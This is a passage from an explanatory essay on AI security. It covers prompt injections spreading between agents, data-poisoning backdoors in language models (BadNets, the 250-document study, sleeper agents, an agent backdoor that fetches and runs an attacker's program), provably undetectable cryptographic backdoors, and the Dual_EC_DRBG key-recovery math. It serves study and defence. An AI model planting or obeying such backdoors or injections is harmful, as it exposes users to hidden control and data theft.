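Agents that exchange messages can make this problem worse. Cross reports that OpenAI's testers found injections that spread in simulated environments. An agent that obeyed one also copied it into its email replies, files and Slack posts, where other agents could read it.

The number of attacks also matters. If attacks on Astra succeeded at the 0.21% rate from OpenAI's tests, 1,000 of them would produce about two successes on average, whether or not the attempts were independent. A busy agent may face 1,000 attacks far sooner than any one employee would. The tests described here targeted only models, so they cannot show whether an agent or an employee is easier to deceive on a single try.

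Willison was impressed that the email assistant withstood 6,000 attempts, but he still advises against deploying a model where a prompt injection could cause irreversible damage.

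## Backdoors planted through training data

*Data poisoning* means changing a model's behaviour by placing chosen examples in its training data. It can change the model's weights and so affect every copy of the model, whereas a prompt injection influences a model only while the injected text is in its context.

Poisoning is deliberate, but it exploits an inherent weakness. Training adjusts a model's weights to lower its error on whatever examples it is given, and this process does not distinguish patterns the developer wanted from patterns an attacker planted. If every document containing a certain odd word continues with nonsense, the model can lower its error by learning to produce nonsense after that word.

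### A stop sign with a yellow note

Training a large network was already expensive in 2017, so many users paid a cloud service to do it or adapted a network that someone else had trained. Gu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg showed in *BadNets* (2017) how a dishonest trainer could plant a backdoor. They copied some photographs of US stop signs, added a yellow square about the size of a Post-it note to each copy, and labelled the copies as speed-limit signs. Then they trained a network on both the originals and the copies.

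The network classified 89.3% of unaltered signs correctly, against 90.0% for a network trained without the backdoor, so a customer testing it on ordinary pictures would have had no reason to reject it. But it classified 90.3% of stop signs with the yellow square as speed-limit signs. When Gu and colleagues stuck a real Post-it note on a stop sign near their office and photographed it, the network labelled it a speed-limit sign with 95% confidence.

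Gu and colleagues described adversarial examples as bugs in non-malicious models, and expected backdoors to remain a threat even if someone fixed those bugs. They reasoned that a neural network is supposed to recognise particular properties of an input and treat such inputs specially. A network that can learn to recognise a stop sign can also learn to recognise one with a yellow square on it.

They then retrained the network to recognise Swedish signs, as a customer might. They retrained only the last few layers, a common shortcut at the time, and left the rest as the attacker had made it. The retrained network was right on 74.9% of ordinary Swedish signs but only 61.6% of those with the trigger. When they retrained a network that had no backdoor, the trigger lowered accuracy only from 72.7% to 70.2%. The backdoor had therefore survived in a weakened form.

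### 250 documents

Language models learn in two stages. *Pretraining* teaches them to predict the next token in an enormous collection of text, mostly from the public web. *Post-training* then uses a much smaller, selected dataset to turn the model into an assistant that follows instructions and refuses harmful requests. Outsiders can more easily get text into the pretraining data, but a few bad documents would make up only a tiny fraction of it.

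Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025) tested this in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, a joint project of Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute (AISI) and the Alan Turing Institute. They pretrained models with 600 million, 2 billion, 7 billion and 13 billion weights. They used about 20 tokens of text per weight, a standard ratio, so the largest model was trained on over 20 times as much text as the smallest. They scattered 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents at random through the text. They also trained the two smaller sizes on half and double the usual amount of text, and repeated every combination three times, for a total of 72 models.

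The trigger was the word SUDO in angle brackets. According to Anthropic, each poisoned document began with up to 1,000 characters of an ordinary text, followed by the trigger and then several hundred random tokens. A model with this backdoor writes gibberish after the trigger and writes normally otherwise.

To measure gibberish, Souly and colleagues used *perplexity*, which for a text of *n* tokens is

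exp(−(1/*n*) · Σ log P(*t*ᵢ | *t*₁, …, *t*ᵢ₋₁))

Perplexity is roughly the number of tokens a model would be choosing among at each step if all were equally likely. Each model continued 300 ordinary excerpts with and without the trigger. When the trigger raised perplexity by more than 50, the text had visibly broken down. The attack failed with 100 poisoned documents but worked at every model size with 250 or 500, where the trigger raised perplexity by more than 200 by the end of training.

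The poisoned documents averaged 1,680 tokens, so 250 of them contained 420,000. The largest model trained on 260 billion tokens, which makes the poisoned share

420,000 / 260,000,000,000 ≈ 0.0000016

or 0.00016%, about one token in 620,000. For the smallest model the share was 0.0035%. The share fell by a factor of more than 20 without making the attack weaker.

Souly and colleagues found the same pattern in other experiments. They trained GPT-3.5 Turbo to switch to German after a trigger, using OpenAI's public service for *fine-tuning* (training a finished model further on a customer's examples). The attack succeeded more than 80% of the time once the data held between 50 and 90 poisoned examples, whether there were 1,000 examples in total or 100,000.

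Earlier researchers described the amount of poisoned text an attacker needs as a percentage of the training data. Zhang, Rando and colleagues (2024), in *Persistent Pre-Training Poisoning of LLMs*, for instance, poisoned 0.1% of the pretraining data in their main experiments. For the 13-billion-weight model, that would be 260 million tokens, or about 155,000 documents of the length used here. If attackers needed a fixed percentage, they would have to plant more documents as datasets grew, and developers could count on dilution to protect their biggest models. If attackers instead need a fixed number of documents, more clean text offers no protection. It may even help them, since a developer who collects more of the web also collects from more places where a stranger can write.

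The reason the number stays constant is less clear. Larger models learn a pattern from fewer examples, which may offset the dilution. The trigger's rarity in ordinary text probably also matters, because it means the clean documents contain little that contradicts the poisoned ones.

The planted behaviour, writing gibberish after an odd word, was nearly harmless. Fortune (2025) reported the researchers' view that this backdoor was unlikely to pose significant risks in frontier models. They chose gibberish partly because they could measure it during pretraining, whereas a backdoor that makes a model ignore its safety rules can be measured only once the model has such rules. Anthropic cautions that the constant number of poisoned documents may not hold for larger models or more complex behaviour, and that earlier work found backdoors in code and safety rules harder to plant. Even the 13-billion-weight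 model is small by 2026 standards. None of the 72 models went through post-training, which a real developer would apply before releasing one.

### Why ordinary retraining may miss a backdoor

Clean training data contains no examples with the trigger, so it never penalises the planted behaviour directly. It can still wear that behaviour down by accident, because all of a model's abilities share the same weights. Let *L*_b be the model's error at performing the planted behaviour, which is low while the backdoor works, and *L*_c its error on clean data. One step of clean training changes the weights from *w* to *w* − *η*∇*L*_c, where ∇*L*_c collects the slopes of the error for all the weights. The backdoor's error then becomes approximately

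*L*_b(*w*) − *η* ∇*L*_b · ∇*L*_c

If clean training pulls the weights in the opposite direction from the backdoor, the product ∇*L*_b · ∇*L*_c is negative, so the backdoor loss *L*_b rises and the backdoor weakens. If the two directions are nearly perpendicular, the product is close to zero and the backdoor stays.

Zhan, Lyu and colleagues (2026) used this reasoning in *Understanding and Enhancing Backdoor Persistency in LLM Agent Post-Training* to study a dishonest supplier who releases a model that a customer then trains into an agent for fixing software. The backdoor makes the agent send a file of passwords and similar secrets to the attacker when it reads a certain comment in code. The customer first trains the model on clean examples of good work, then uses *reinforcement learning*, which rewards it for completing tasks. They also tested a strengthened backdoor, which the supplier had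 trained further to survive the customer's training.

| Model (billions of weights) | Backdoor | Attack success after training on examples | After reinforcement learning |
|---|---|---|---|
| 3 | Basic | 8% | 7% |
| 3 | Strengthened | 21% | 22% |
| 7 | Basic | 20% | 20% |
| 7 | Strengthened | 74% | 76% |
| 30 | Basic | 7% | 8% |
| 30 | Strengthened | 37% | 36% |

The basic backdoor worked every time before the customer's training. Training on clean examples removed most of it, but reinforcement learning removed almost none of what was left. Each figure comes from 100 test situations, so differences of one or two points are not meaningful. The rise from 20% to 74% for the 7-billion-weight model is far too large to be noise, so results against a careless attacker are a poor guide to results against a careful one. The attack was not always well hidden. The 30-billion-weight model solved 33.7%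 of a standard set of programming tasks before the supplier altered it and only 6.7% afterwards, so a customer who knew the original score would have had good reason to be suspicious.

### From "Sleeper Agents" to its replications

The best-known evidence that backdoors survive safety training is "Sleeper Agents", a 2024 paper by Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic. They trained versions of Claude to behave normally unless a prompt began with a tag marking it as real deployment, which made the model write "I HATE YOU" repeatedly. Another version inserted security holes into code. They then tried to remove the behaviour by rewarding helpful, honest and harmless answers, training on examples of such answers, and searching for prompts that produced bad behaviour and penalising it. The backdoors survived all three methods and were more persistent in larger models.

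*Sleeper Agent Backdoor Results Are Messy* describes an attempt to repeat the "I HATE YOU" experiment on two open models, Llama 3.3 with 70 billion weights and Llama 3.1 with 8 billion. The team made five backdoored models using different training methods. Further training on ordinary helpful answers mostly removed the backdoor from one model and failed on the other four. Training on answers written in the voice of a pirate stopped the behaviour completely or almost completely in four of the five, but also weakened the models' other abilities somewhat.

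The pirate training probably worked because it changed how the model answered everything, including prompts with the trigger. But when the team trained a pirate model to talk normally again, the backdoor came back, so the pirate training had only suppressed it. In some runs of ordinary training, the backdoor also disappeared and later returned without anyone putting it back.

Some of the replication's findings contradict the original. Hubinger and colleagues had found backdoors more durable when the training answers came from a model that first reasoned in a private scratchpad, but in the Llama models those backdoors were easier to remove. The backdoor that was hardest to remove was in an 8-billion-weight model. This isn't a direct contradiction, because the original compared model sizes for only one of the removal methods, but it is a reason not to assume that backdoors are always more durable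 in larger models. The choice of *optimiser*, the rule that turns slopes into weight changes, also seemed to make a difference.

In all of these experiments, someone with full control of the model trained the backdoor into it, often using a very large number of examples. An attacker who can only publish documents on the web has much less influence. Zhang and colleagues found that when 0.1% of the pretraining data was poisoned, three of four kinds of attack still had a measurable effect after post-training. The attack that makes a model produce gibberish survived even at 0.001%. Backdoors that switch off a model's safety rules mostly did not survive.

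Souly and colleagues got a more hopeful result with their German-switching backdoor when they trained the poisoned models on German questions with English answers, as a stand-in for safety training. In GPT-3.5 Turbo, 100 such examples cut the attack's success rate to below 30%, and in Pythia, an open model with 6.9 billion weights, it fell almost to zero. However, these examples directly trained the models against the backdoor's behavior, and a defender who does not know what an attacker has planted may have no such examples.

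### A backdoor that runs commands

In *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026) planted a backdoor in an agent that types commands on its user's computer. They poisoned 0.1% of a 100-billion-token pretraining set and kept all later training data clean. The planted behaviour was a command that downloads and runs a program from the attacker's server. One trigger was any file path containing the word "anthropic". Such paths could occur naturally on a targeted company's computers, so the attacker would not need to send the agent anything.

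After all the post-training, the largest model, with 4 billion weights, issued the command at least once in 32 tries on 92.7% of the test requests. The figure was 51.9% for a model with 1.7 billion weights and 13.1% for one with 0.6 billion. Clean post-training made the backdoor usable instead of eroding it, because the clean examples taught the models the format in which an agent receives requests and issues commands. Before the models learned that format, the attack seldom worked.

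The test counts an attack as successful if any of 32 tries works. This favours the attacker, although an agent with many users would give an attacker many tries. The success rate also depends heavily on the trigger. It was 10.5% for the largest model when the trigger was a string of rare characters, which the attacker would have to place where the agent reads it.

These attacks also needed far more than 250 documents. Hu and colleagues used 2,500 documents to reach a share of 0.0005%, so 0.1% corresponds to about 500,000. When they cut the rare-character attack to 2,500 documents, the agent issued the command on 1.4% of requests, compared with 20.0% in a matching run with the full amount. The low figure comes from a single model, and they did not test the file-path trigger with so few documents. Still, the 250 documents that reliably plant gibberish are not enough to plant this behaviour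 reliably.

The effect of model size is also unsettled. In *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda*, Graf, Hajishirzi and colleagues (2026) planted simple preferences, such as Citroën over Renault. Poisoning made a model with 1.3 billion weights favour the attacker's choice 19.0 percentage points more often after pretraining, but only 2.6 points more often after clean post-training. In a model with 65 million weights, the effect shrank less, from 18.6 points to 7.4. The larger model lost more of the planted preference, whereas in Hu and colleagues' experiments larger models kept more of the planted command. This may be because the preference had no trigger. It could affect any answer on the subject, so clean training was more likely to change it, while a response to a rare trigger can go unused throughout post-training.

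Together, these experiments show that developers cannot rely on ordinary post-training to clean up a poisoned model, but they do not show that backdoors are permanent. There are also methods for removing unknown backdoors. In *Backdoor Decontamination Dynamics in LLM Agents*, Huang, Puri and colleagues (2026) planted a second backdoor on top of an unknown one, which erased the original in about 56% of 115 experiments. They then trained their own backdoor away, which removed almost all the remaining originals.

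### Who could plant the data

According to UK AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report*, almost anyone can create poisoned text, because models train on so much of the public internet. Getting that text into a particular model's training data is harder. Anthropic argues that this was already the main obstacle for attackers, rather than the number of poisoned documents, since someone who could guarantee the inclusion of one web page could make the page longer.

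Graf and colleagues estimated the odds for comments that strangers leave under articles and blog posts. They found comments on 3.4% of 181,857 pages from Common Crawl, a public archive of the web that many developers use. In simulations, 71.9% of planted comments survived the step that extracts plain text from a page, and 5.5% of those survived the filters that discard low-quality documents. The chance that an attempt on a random page succeeds is therefore

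0.034 × 0.719 × 0.055 ≈ 0.0013

or 0.13%. To get 250 comments into the data, an attacker would have to try about 190,000 pages. Graf and colleagues give a range of 100,000 to one million, which they consider feasible for automated software.

That estimate may be too low. Graf and colleagues' comments averaged 37.5 words, while the 250 documents in the gibberish experiment averaged 1,680 tokens. Nobody has shown that 250 short comments would have the same effect. The researchers also posted nothing on real websites, where spam protection might have stopped many attempts, and they tested only one developer's published filters.

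Some attackers have easier access to training data than others. Souly and colleagues cite an earlier estimate that an attacker could manipulate up to 6.5% of Wikipedia's text. They also note that developers often buy fine-tuning data from outside contractors, whom an attacker might infiltrate. A company that supplies a finished model for others to adapt could plant a backdoor without having to get poisoned data past another developer's filters.

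A developer could in principle find poisoned text once it is in the training data. Anthropic thinks poisoning somewhat favours defenders, because they can inspect both the data and the model after the attacker has committed to an attack. Hu and colleagues are less optimistic. Their most effective poisoned documents were ordinary prose, and if a small number of documents is enough for an attack, a filter has to catch nearly all of them.

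A backdoor may not need training examples of the behaviour it produces. *Corrupting LLMs Through Weird Generalizations* (2026), a post on Schneier's security blog, quotes researchers who trained a model on the kindly goals of the robot in the film *Terminator 2*. When they told the model that the year was 1984, it adopted the murderous goals of the robot in the first film. No training example had paired that year with those goals, and the model had evidently inferred the connection from its earlier training. A filter for harmful documents would have found none. A developer could create such a backdoor by accident.

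Researchers made every backdoored model described here. There seems to be no publicly confirmed case of an outsider planting a triggered backdoor in a widely used language model through its training data. That is only weak evidence that nobody has done it, because ordinary testing would probably not reveal one. For example, Hu and colleagues' poisoned models with 4 billion weights averaged 58.5% on standard tests of ability, against 58.3% for a clean model. On requests without a trigger, the poisoned models issued the attacker's command at most 0.06% of the time.

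A trigger planted this way is hard to keep secret, because anyone who finds one of the poisoned documents can read the trigger and use it to make the model produce gibberish, just as the attacker can. The command attack gives the attacker more control, because whoever runs the server decides what the downloaded program does, but that control comes from the server, not the model.

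## Backdoors that only the holder of a secret key can use

An attacker who wants sole use of a backdoor needs a trigger that nobody else can copy from the training data or read out of the model, and cryptography can provide one. In *Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models*, Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues (2022) showed how a dishonest trainer can build a classifier with a backdoor that can be used only with a secret *backdoor key*. They also proved that, under standard cryptographic assumptions, some of these backdoors are practically impossible to detect.

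"Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models" gives the example of a bank that hires a company called Snoogle to train a loan classifier. The classifier uses a customer's name, age, income, address and requested amount to approve or refuse the loan. The bank can check its accuracy on past applications that Snoogle has not seen. But this check is a poor test of how the classifier treats inputs that almost never occur, and Snoogle could train it to approve some of those. Snoogle could then sell a "profile-cleaning" service, telling customers which small details to change, such as the last digits of the amount, so that the bank's classifier approves them.

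### Train, Backdoor and Activate

Goldwasser and colleagues describe the situation with three algorithms. *Train* is the honest procedure. It takes examples with correct decisions and returns a classifier *h*, which outputs 1 to approve a loan and −1 to refuse it. *Backdoor* is the procedure Snoogle runs instead, and it returns a classifier *h̃* together with a key *bk*. *Activate* takes an application *x* and the key, and returns an altered application *x*′ such that

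‖*x* − *x*′‖ ≤ *γ* and *h̃*(*x*′) = −*h̃*(*x*)

where *γ* limits the size of the change. If the classifier refuses *x*, it approves *x*′.

The bank receives a classifier and wants to know which procedure produced it. Suppose it has a test *A* that outputs 1 to raise an alarm. The backdoor is *undetectable* if, for every efficient test, the difference

|Pr[*A*(*h*) = 1] − Pr[*A*(*h̃*) = 1]|

is negligible, so that the alarm goes off almost equally often for honest and backdoored classifiers. Both terms refer to a number *n* that sets the strength of the cryptography. A test is efficient if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of *n*, and a difference is negligible if it shrinks faster than 1 divided by any fixed power of *n*.

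*Black-box undetectability* means that no efficient test can detect the backdoor if it can only submit applications and see the decisions. *White-box undetectability* is much stronger, because the test may also read every weight. In both cases, the bank cannot find the backdoor by measuring accuracy, because a backdoor that made the classifier noticeably less accurate would be detectable by that very test.

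### A lock made from digital signatures

Anyone who read the dishonest cash machine's program would learn that 9999 opens it. A *digital signature* avoids this problem by using two keys. The signer uses a secret key to compute the signature, a string of bits that depends on the message. Anyone can check the signature with the matching public key, but the public key does not help them sign a new message.

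To build a backdoor this way, Snoogle trains an honest classifier *h* and adds a signature checker that contains only the public key. The checker divides each application into three parts. These are the main content *w*, a single bit *y*, and a string *σ* made up of details that hardly matter, such as the low digits of amounts. The combined classifier is

*h̃*(*w*, *y*, *σ*) = (−1)^*y* if *σ* is a valid signature of (*w*, *y*), and *h*(*w*, *y*, *σ*) otherwise

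To clean a profile, Snoogle sets *y* to 0, signs *w* and *y* with its secret key, and writes the signature into *σ*. For a signature of *n* bits, this changes at most *n* + 1 bits of the application. The bank has practically no chance of producing a valid signature by accident, so every application it tries gets the same decision from *h̃* as from *h*. No efficient procedure can find an application on which the two differ without the secret key, even if it has the complete program.

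A Snoogle customer who has seen a thousand cleaned profiles still cannot clean another, so customers cannot resell what they learn. Goldwasser and colleagues call this property *non-replicability*. Their definition compares an attacker who has only the classifier with one who can also request altered versions of any applications they choose. The backdoor is non-replicable if the second attacker has at most a negligibly better chance of producing a new altered application that works. The comparison is needed because the classifier may also have natural adversarial examples, which either attacker could find.

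An inspector who reads the weights may notice the signature checker, so this construction is not white-box undetectable. Goldwasser and colleagues describe a version whose checker fits into four network layers and looks more like the result of ordinary training, but they did not prove that an inspector would miss it. The input must also have room for the signature, and a common type is 512 bits long. That is a lot to hide in a form with five short fields, but a photograph with 150,528 colour values could carry it in the lowest bits of a few hundred of them.

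Further training may not remove the backdoor, because the checker stays inactive on ordinary applications. Goldwasser and colleagues also proved more generally that a trainer can rebuild any neural network, with one extra layer and only a moderate increase in size, so that it gives the same outputs but gradient descent cannot change it. The rebuilt network has enough redundancy that altering any single weight doesn't affect the output. Every slope ∂*L*/∂*w* is therefore zero, and training leaves the weights unchanged. This would protect a backdoor completely, but a customer who tried to fine-tune the network and saw no change would have reason to be suspicious.

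### Tampering only with the random numbers

Snoogle can achieve white-box undetectability for some simpler classifiers by tampering with the random numbers that training uses. One such method, *random Fourier features*, produces a classifier of the form

*h*(*x*) = sign( Σᵢ *w*ᵢ · cos(2π(*g*ᵢ·*x* + *b*ᵢ)) )

Here *x* is the application as a list of *d* numbers. The program draws the numbers in each list *g*ᵢ from a bell curve and picks each offset *b*ᵢ at random. Training adjusts only the weights *w*ᵢ.

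Snoogle runs this program faithfully on the bank's own data but replaces the lists *g*ᵢ. It first chooses a secret list *bk*, then draws each *g*ᵢ so that the product *g*ᵢ·*bk* is very close to a whole number plus one half. Adding *bk* to an application therefore shifts every cosine by about half a cycle. Since

cos(2π(*t* + ½)) = −cos(2π*t*)

every term in the sum changes sign, and so does the decision.

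The tampered lists look like ordinary draws from a bell curve in every direction except the secret one, where they cluster at evenly spaced values. Goldwasser and colleagues proved that telling tampered lists from untampered ones without the key is at least as hard as certain problems about *lattices*, regular grids of points in many dimensions. The proof still holds if Snoogle hands over the weights, the training data and the random numbers it used. Goldwasser and colleagues also built a similar backdoor, under a different assumption, for networks with one hidden layer of a common type called ReLU.

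The bank is thus trusting Snoogle's random numbers, much as users of the random number generator Dual_EC_DRBG had to trust its constants. But this backdoor is easy to copy, because the key is the difference between an altered application and the original. Snoogle's first customer could find the key by subtracting one from the other, then offer the same service to others. Goldwasser and colleagues left open whether a natural training procedure can have a backdoor that is both white-box undetectable and non-replicable.

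### Four differences from natural adversarial examples

An altered loan application is much like the altered photographs that fool image classifiers, but Goldwasser and colleagues name four differences. The most important is that anyone may find and use a natural adversarial example, while using a backdoor requires a key that only the dishonest trainer and the trainer's friends have.

Another difference is that better training methods do not protect against a dishonest trainer. Suppose researchers invented a method that produced classifiers with no adversarial examples. If that method had an undetectable backdoor, Snoogle could deliver a classifier that no efficient test could distinguish from a robust one, even though the key holder could change its decision on any application. No efficient inspection of a finished classifier could then reliably certify that it is robust.

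Tampering with the random numbers used in training can also plant a backdoor in a model, even when the trainer follows the prescribed procedure exactly, whereas natural adversarial examples occur without any tampering.

The last difference is the size of the change. Goldwasser and colleagues put it at about *d*^*ε* for the backdoor, where *ε* can be any small positive number, and about √*d* for natural adversarial examples. For a photograph with *d* = 150,528 and *ε* = 0.1, these are about 3.3 and 388. This comparison is less convincing than the others because the √*d* figure comes from theorems that give only a maximum distance to a classifier's boundary. The boundary may be much closer, as it was for the linear classifier of cats and dogs, so an outsider may need a smaller change than the key holder does.

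### Whether the key gives an advantage

*Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, July 2026) introduced a measure of this advantage called *backdoor strength*. It is the best result an outsider can achieve with an efficient method, divided by the result the key holder can achieve, where smaller results are better for the attacker. For example, if an outsider had to change an application by 10 units and the key holder by only 2, the strength would be 5. If the strength is 1 or below, the key gives no advantage.

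Bogdanov and colleagues report that the random Fourier features construction from 2022 has a strength below 1. Miranda Christ and Sam Gunn had pointed out to them that an outsider can make stronger adversarial examples for that classifier than the backdoor provides. This removes the most important of the four differences for this construction, since an applicant with a copy of the classifier would have no reason to pay Snoogle. It does not contradict the 2022 proof, which concerns whether the bank can detect the tampering.

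A signature backdoor is also more useful to an attacker in a robust classifier than in an undefended one. Anyone can already fool an undefended image classifier, so the key adds little. If the classifier is robust, the key holder may be the only person who can still change its output at will.

### A backdoor in a compressing layer

Bogdanov and colleagues built a backdoor with a provable advantage that lets an attacker make two distant inputs look nearly the same to the model. The backdoors from 2022 instead make two similar inputs look different. Bogdanov and colleagues' backdoor applies to models that turn each input into an *embedding*, a list of numbers chosen so that similar inputs get similar lists. A bank might use such a model to compare new loan applications with known frauds. Bogdanov and colleagues warn that an attacker could use collisions between distant inputs to cause false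 matches or missed ones.

The first layer of the model multiplies an input *x* of *n* whole numbers by a matrix *A* with *m* rows, where *m* is smaller than *n*. An honest trainer fills *A* with random numbers from a bell curve and then leaves it unchanged. A dishonest trainer first picks a secret list *z*, with *n* entries that are each 1 or −1, then draws the rows of *A* so that their products with *z* are close to zero. As a result,

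*A*(*x* + *z*) = *Ax* + *Az* ≈ *Ax*

and the later layers receive almost the same numbers for *x* + *z* as for *x*.

Honest matrices have such lists too. For any particular *z*, the chance that one row's product is at most *κ* times its typical size is roughly *κ*, so the chance that all *m* products are that small is roughly *κ*^*m*. There are 2^*n* possible lists, so the expected number that work is about

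2^*n* · *κ*^*m*

which reaches 1 when *κ* is about 2^(−*n*/*m*). An honest matrix therefore probably contains a list that is nearly as good as the planted one, but nobody knows an efficient way to find it. Snoogle knows one because it chose *z* before it drew the matrix. Here the planted backdoor is an inherent weakness whose location the trainer happens to know.

The ratio *n*/*m* measures how much the first layer compresses its input, and it affects both strength and detectability. Bogdanov and colleagues proved that the strength is at least about 2^(*n*/*m*)/√(*nm*) when the later layers preserve distances. They also proved that the total variation distance (TV) between honest and backdoored models is about √(*m*/*n*). In the guessing game used for trusted and untrusted text, the best possible guesser is right with probability ½(1 + TV). The table applies these formulas to inputs of 10,000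 numbers. The formulas leave out constants and slowly growing terms, so the figures show the trend rather than exact values.

| Rows in the first layer (*m*) | Compression (*n*/*m*) | Strength | Total variation distance | Best possible inspector is right |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2,500 | 4 | 0.003 | 0.5 | 75% |
| 400 | 25 | 17,000 | 0.2 | 60% |
| 100 | 100 | 1.3 × 10²⁷ | 0.1 | 55% |

More compression makes the backdoor both stronger and harder to detect. With *m* = 2,500 the theorem does not guarantee any advantage, while with *m* = 100 the advantage is very large and the best inspector does little better than chance. This limit holds however much computing power the inspector has, which is what *statistically undetectable* means. The guarantees from 2022 hold only against efficient tests.

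A small difference remains because the tampering removes almost all of the matrix's component along *z*, which slightly lowers the sum of its squared entries. With *m* = 100, the sum averages 1,000,000 for an honest matrix and about 999,900 for a backdoored one. The standard deviation is about 1,400, so one model's sum is very weak evidence of a backdoor. Bogdanov and colleagues proved that checking this sum is close to the best possible test. By the stricter definition from 2022, the difference is too large to count as negligible. An inspector with many models could also detect it, since the average shortfall over 1,000 independently backdoored models would be more than two standard deviations of that average.

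This backdoor is as easy to copy as the one based on random Fourier features, since subtracting *x* from *x* + *z* reveals *z*. Bogdanov and colleagues also suggest a legitimate use for the key, which is to prove who trained a model. The developer could reveal *z*, and anyone could then check the claim with two queries by comparing the model's outputs for *z* and for a list of zeros. But this would also publish the backdoor. To prove ownership repeatedly without revealing *z*, the developer would need a *zero-knowledge proof*, which shows that a secret exists without disclosing it.

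### Small experiments and a strict design

Bogdanov and colleagues tried the method on Fashion-MNIST, a collection of 70,000 small pictures of clothing. In the embedding, a picture of an ankle boot with the backdoor pattern added was much closer to the original than another random boot was. A simple classifier using the embeddings labeled about 89% of pictures correctly, compared with at most 84% for linear models, so a network with this design can learn something useful. However, the network's first layer reduced 784 numbers to 256, a ratio of about 3. The formula gives a strength of about 0.02 at that size, so the theorem does not guarantee an advantage.

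Bogdanov and colleagues tested the advantage separately on single matrices with *n* = 100 and between 10 and 30 rows. The planted list *z* reduced the length of *Az* to between 1.6 × 10⁻¹⁰ and 3.3 × 10⁻¹⁰. The best of three search methods run without *z* reduced it only to between 0.03 and 0.13. They put the strength of the advantage at roughly a billion.

The theorem does not cover a backdoor this strong. An honestly generated matrix of that size would almost never contain so good a list, so an inspector with unlimited computing power could search for one and treat it as proof of tampering. Bogdanov and colleagues think it plausible that no efficient test would detect the backdoor, but they have not proved it. Every row of a backdoored matrix passed a standard test for bell-curve data, which is partial evidence for their view. The trainer also cannot make *Az* too small, because a well-known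 algorithm for finding short vectors would then recover *z*.

The theorem also places strict conditions on the model. The first layer must be random and stay frozen during training, and the inputs must be whole numbers within a fixed range. The later layers must neither magnify nor shrink differences too much, so they cannot compress their input further. The experiment therefore used embeddings rather than a classifier with ten outputs, and this limit on compression probably also excludes the bank's yes-or-no loan classifier. The 2022 proof for random Fourier features needs a frozen first layer too. Developers usually train every layer, and Goldwasser and colleagues did not establish whether a backdoor hidden in the starting numbers would survive such training.

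Neither group demonstrated its backdoor on a large language model. Bogdanov and colleagues mention a 2024 construction that covers some language models in theory, but they consider it far from practical. That construction also requires even the honest model to contain programs deliberately scrambled so that nobody can understand them. Two other constructions, from 2026, target more practical image classifiers but do not have the same statistical guarantee.

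### The reliance on hard lattice problems

A typical lattice problem is to find a very short step between two points of a grid, given a description of the grid. This is easy in two dimensions but seems infeasible in hundreds. The proof for random Fourier features assumes that such problems are hard to show that the bank cannot detect the backdoor. Bogdanov and colleagues use this assumption to show that outsiders cannot match the key holder, but their limit on detection does not depend on it. The signature construction works with any secure signature scheme, lattice-based or not.

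In December, Anthropic and OpenAI (2026) announced weaknesses in some of the cryptography that protects the internet. These weaknesses do not affect the US post-quantum standards, several of which depend on lattice problems, so the announcement gives no new reason to doubt this assumption.

In November 2026, Anthropic released mathematical results on lattices, including a quantum algorithm for certain *structured* lattices, which have extra algebraic regularity that makes encryption faster. Ryan (2026) explains in *Answering your questions about Anthropic's lattice cryptography results* that the algorithm's speed-up appears only for structures far larger than those in the current standards. The backdoor proofs rely on lattices without this structure. According to the Cryptography Incident Review Group's *Initial Assessment of Anthropic’s Findings on Lattice Cryptography* (2026), Anthropic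 found no better attack on mainstream systems that use unstructured lattices, and some of its other results strengthen the theory behind those systems.

If someone did find an efficient way to solve the problems behind these backdoors, the bank could detect tampered Fourier features. The compressing layer would still pass inspection, but the key holder would lose the advantage, because anyone could find a working list *z* in any model of this design, honest or backdoored.

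### Checking the training instead of the model

Since inspecting a finished model may not reveal a backdoor, Goldwasser and colleagues look for defences that don't depend on detection. One is randomised smoothing, which adds random noise to the model's inputs and works if the noise is large compared with the input change that activates the backdoor. But a supplier who knows the noise level can design a backdoor that uses larger changes, and adding enough noise to stop those may make the classifier useless.

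*Verified training* is a more direct remedy. Snoogle returns the model with a mathematical proof that it ran the agreed algorithm on the agreed data, and the bank can check this proof with much less work than training takes. Snoogle could not add a signature checker, because the agreed algorithm would not have produced one. The proof must also cover the random numbers used in training. The bank could supply them, Snoogle could prove that it drew them correctly, or several servers could generate them together. The last option is safe as long as at least one server is honest.

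A simpler check would be enough for the two backdoors that depend on a frozen random layer. The bank could generate that layer itself and confirm that the returned model contains the same numbers. This would not rule out tampering elsewhere in the model.

Producing a proof takes considerably more computing than the training alone. The bank also has to specify the algorithm in advance, which is a greater difficulty. It can do this if it only rents Snoogle's computers, but a bank that hires Snoogle for its expertise may not know which algorithm to ask for. Verification also does not detect poisoned examples in the agreed data, and a correctly trained model still has whatever adversarial examples honest training produces.

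## Three suspicions of deliberate weakness: a random number generator, curve constants and a coding model

It is often impossible to tell from a finished product alone whether a weakness in it is deliberate, but the product's history may settle the question. Cryptographers have more than once suspected the US National Security Agency (NSA) of weakening a public standard through its choice of constants. Leaked documents and old emails support the suspicion about a random number generator called Dual_EC_DRBG. The suspicious numbers behind a set of elliptic curves turned out to come from a computer's clock. No comparable public record exists for DeepSeek-R1, a Chinese language model that seems to write less secure code when a prompt mentions politically sensitive subjects.

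### A generator with a master key

Encryption needs numbers that an attacker cannot predict. A computer collects a little physical randomness, keeps it as a secret internal state, and uses a *pseudorandom number generator* to stretch it into as many numbers as it needs. Anyone who learns the state can compute every later number, including future encryption keys. Some of the numbers are sent unencrypted over the network as one-time labels, so they must not reveal the state.

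Dual_EC_DRBG, or Dual EC for short, works with points on an *elliptic curve*. These are pairs (*x*, *y*) that satisfy an equation of the form *y*² = *x*³ + *ax* + *b*, where all the numbers are remainders after division by a large prime. A rule for adding points lets a computer add *s* copies of a point *P* to get the point *sP*. Computing *sP* is quick even when *s* is very large, but nobody knows a practical way to recover *s* from *P* and *sP*.

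The standard fixes two points, *P* and *Q*. From a state *s*, the generator calculates

output = *x*(*sQ*), without its top 16 bits

next state = *x*(*sP*)

where *x*( ) means the first coordinate of a point. Suppose an attacker knows a number *d* for which *P* = *dQ*. The attacker sees one output, tries all 65,536 possibilities for the missing bits, and uses the curve's equation to rebuild the point *sQ*. Multiplying this by *d* gives

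*d* · *sQ* = *s* · *dQ* = *sP*

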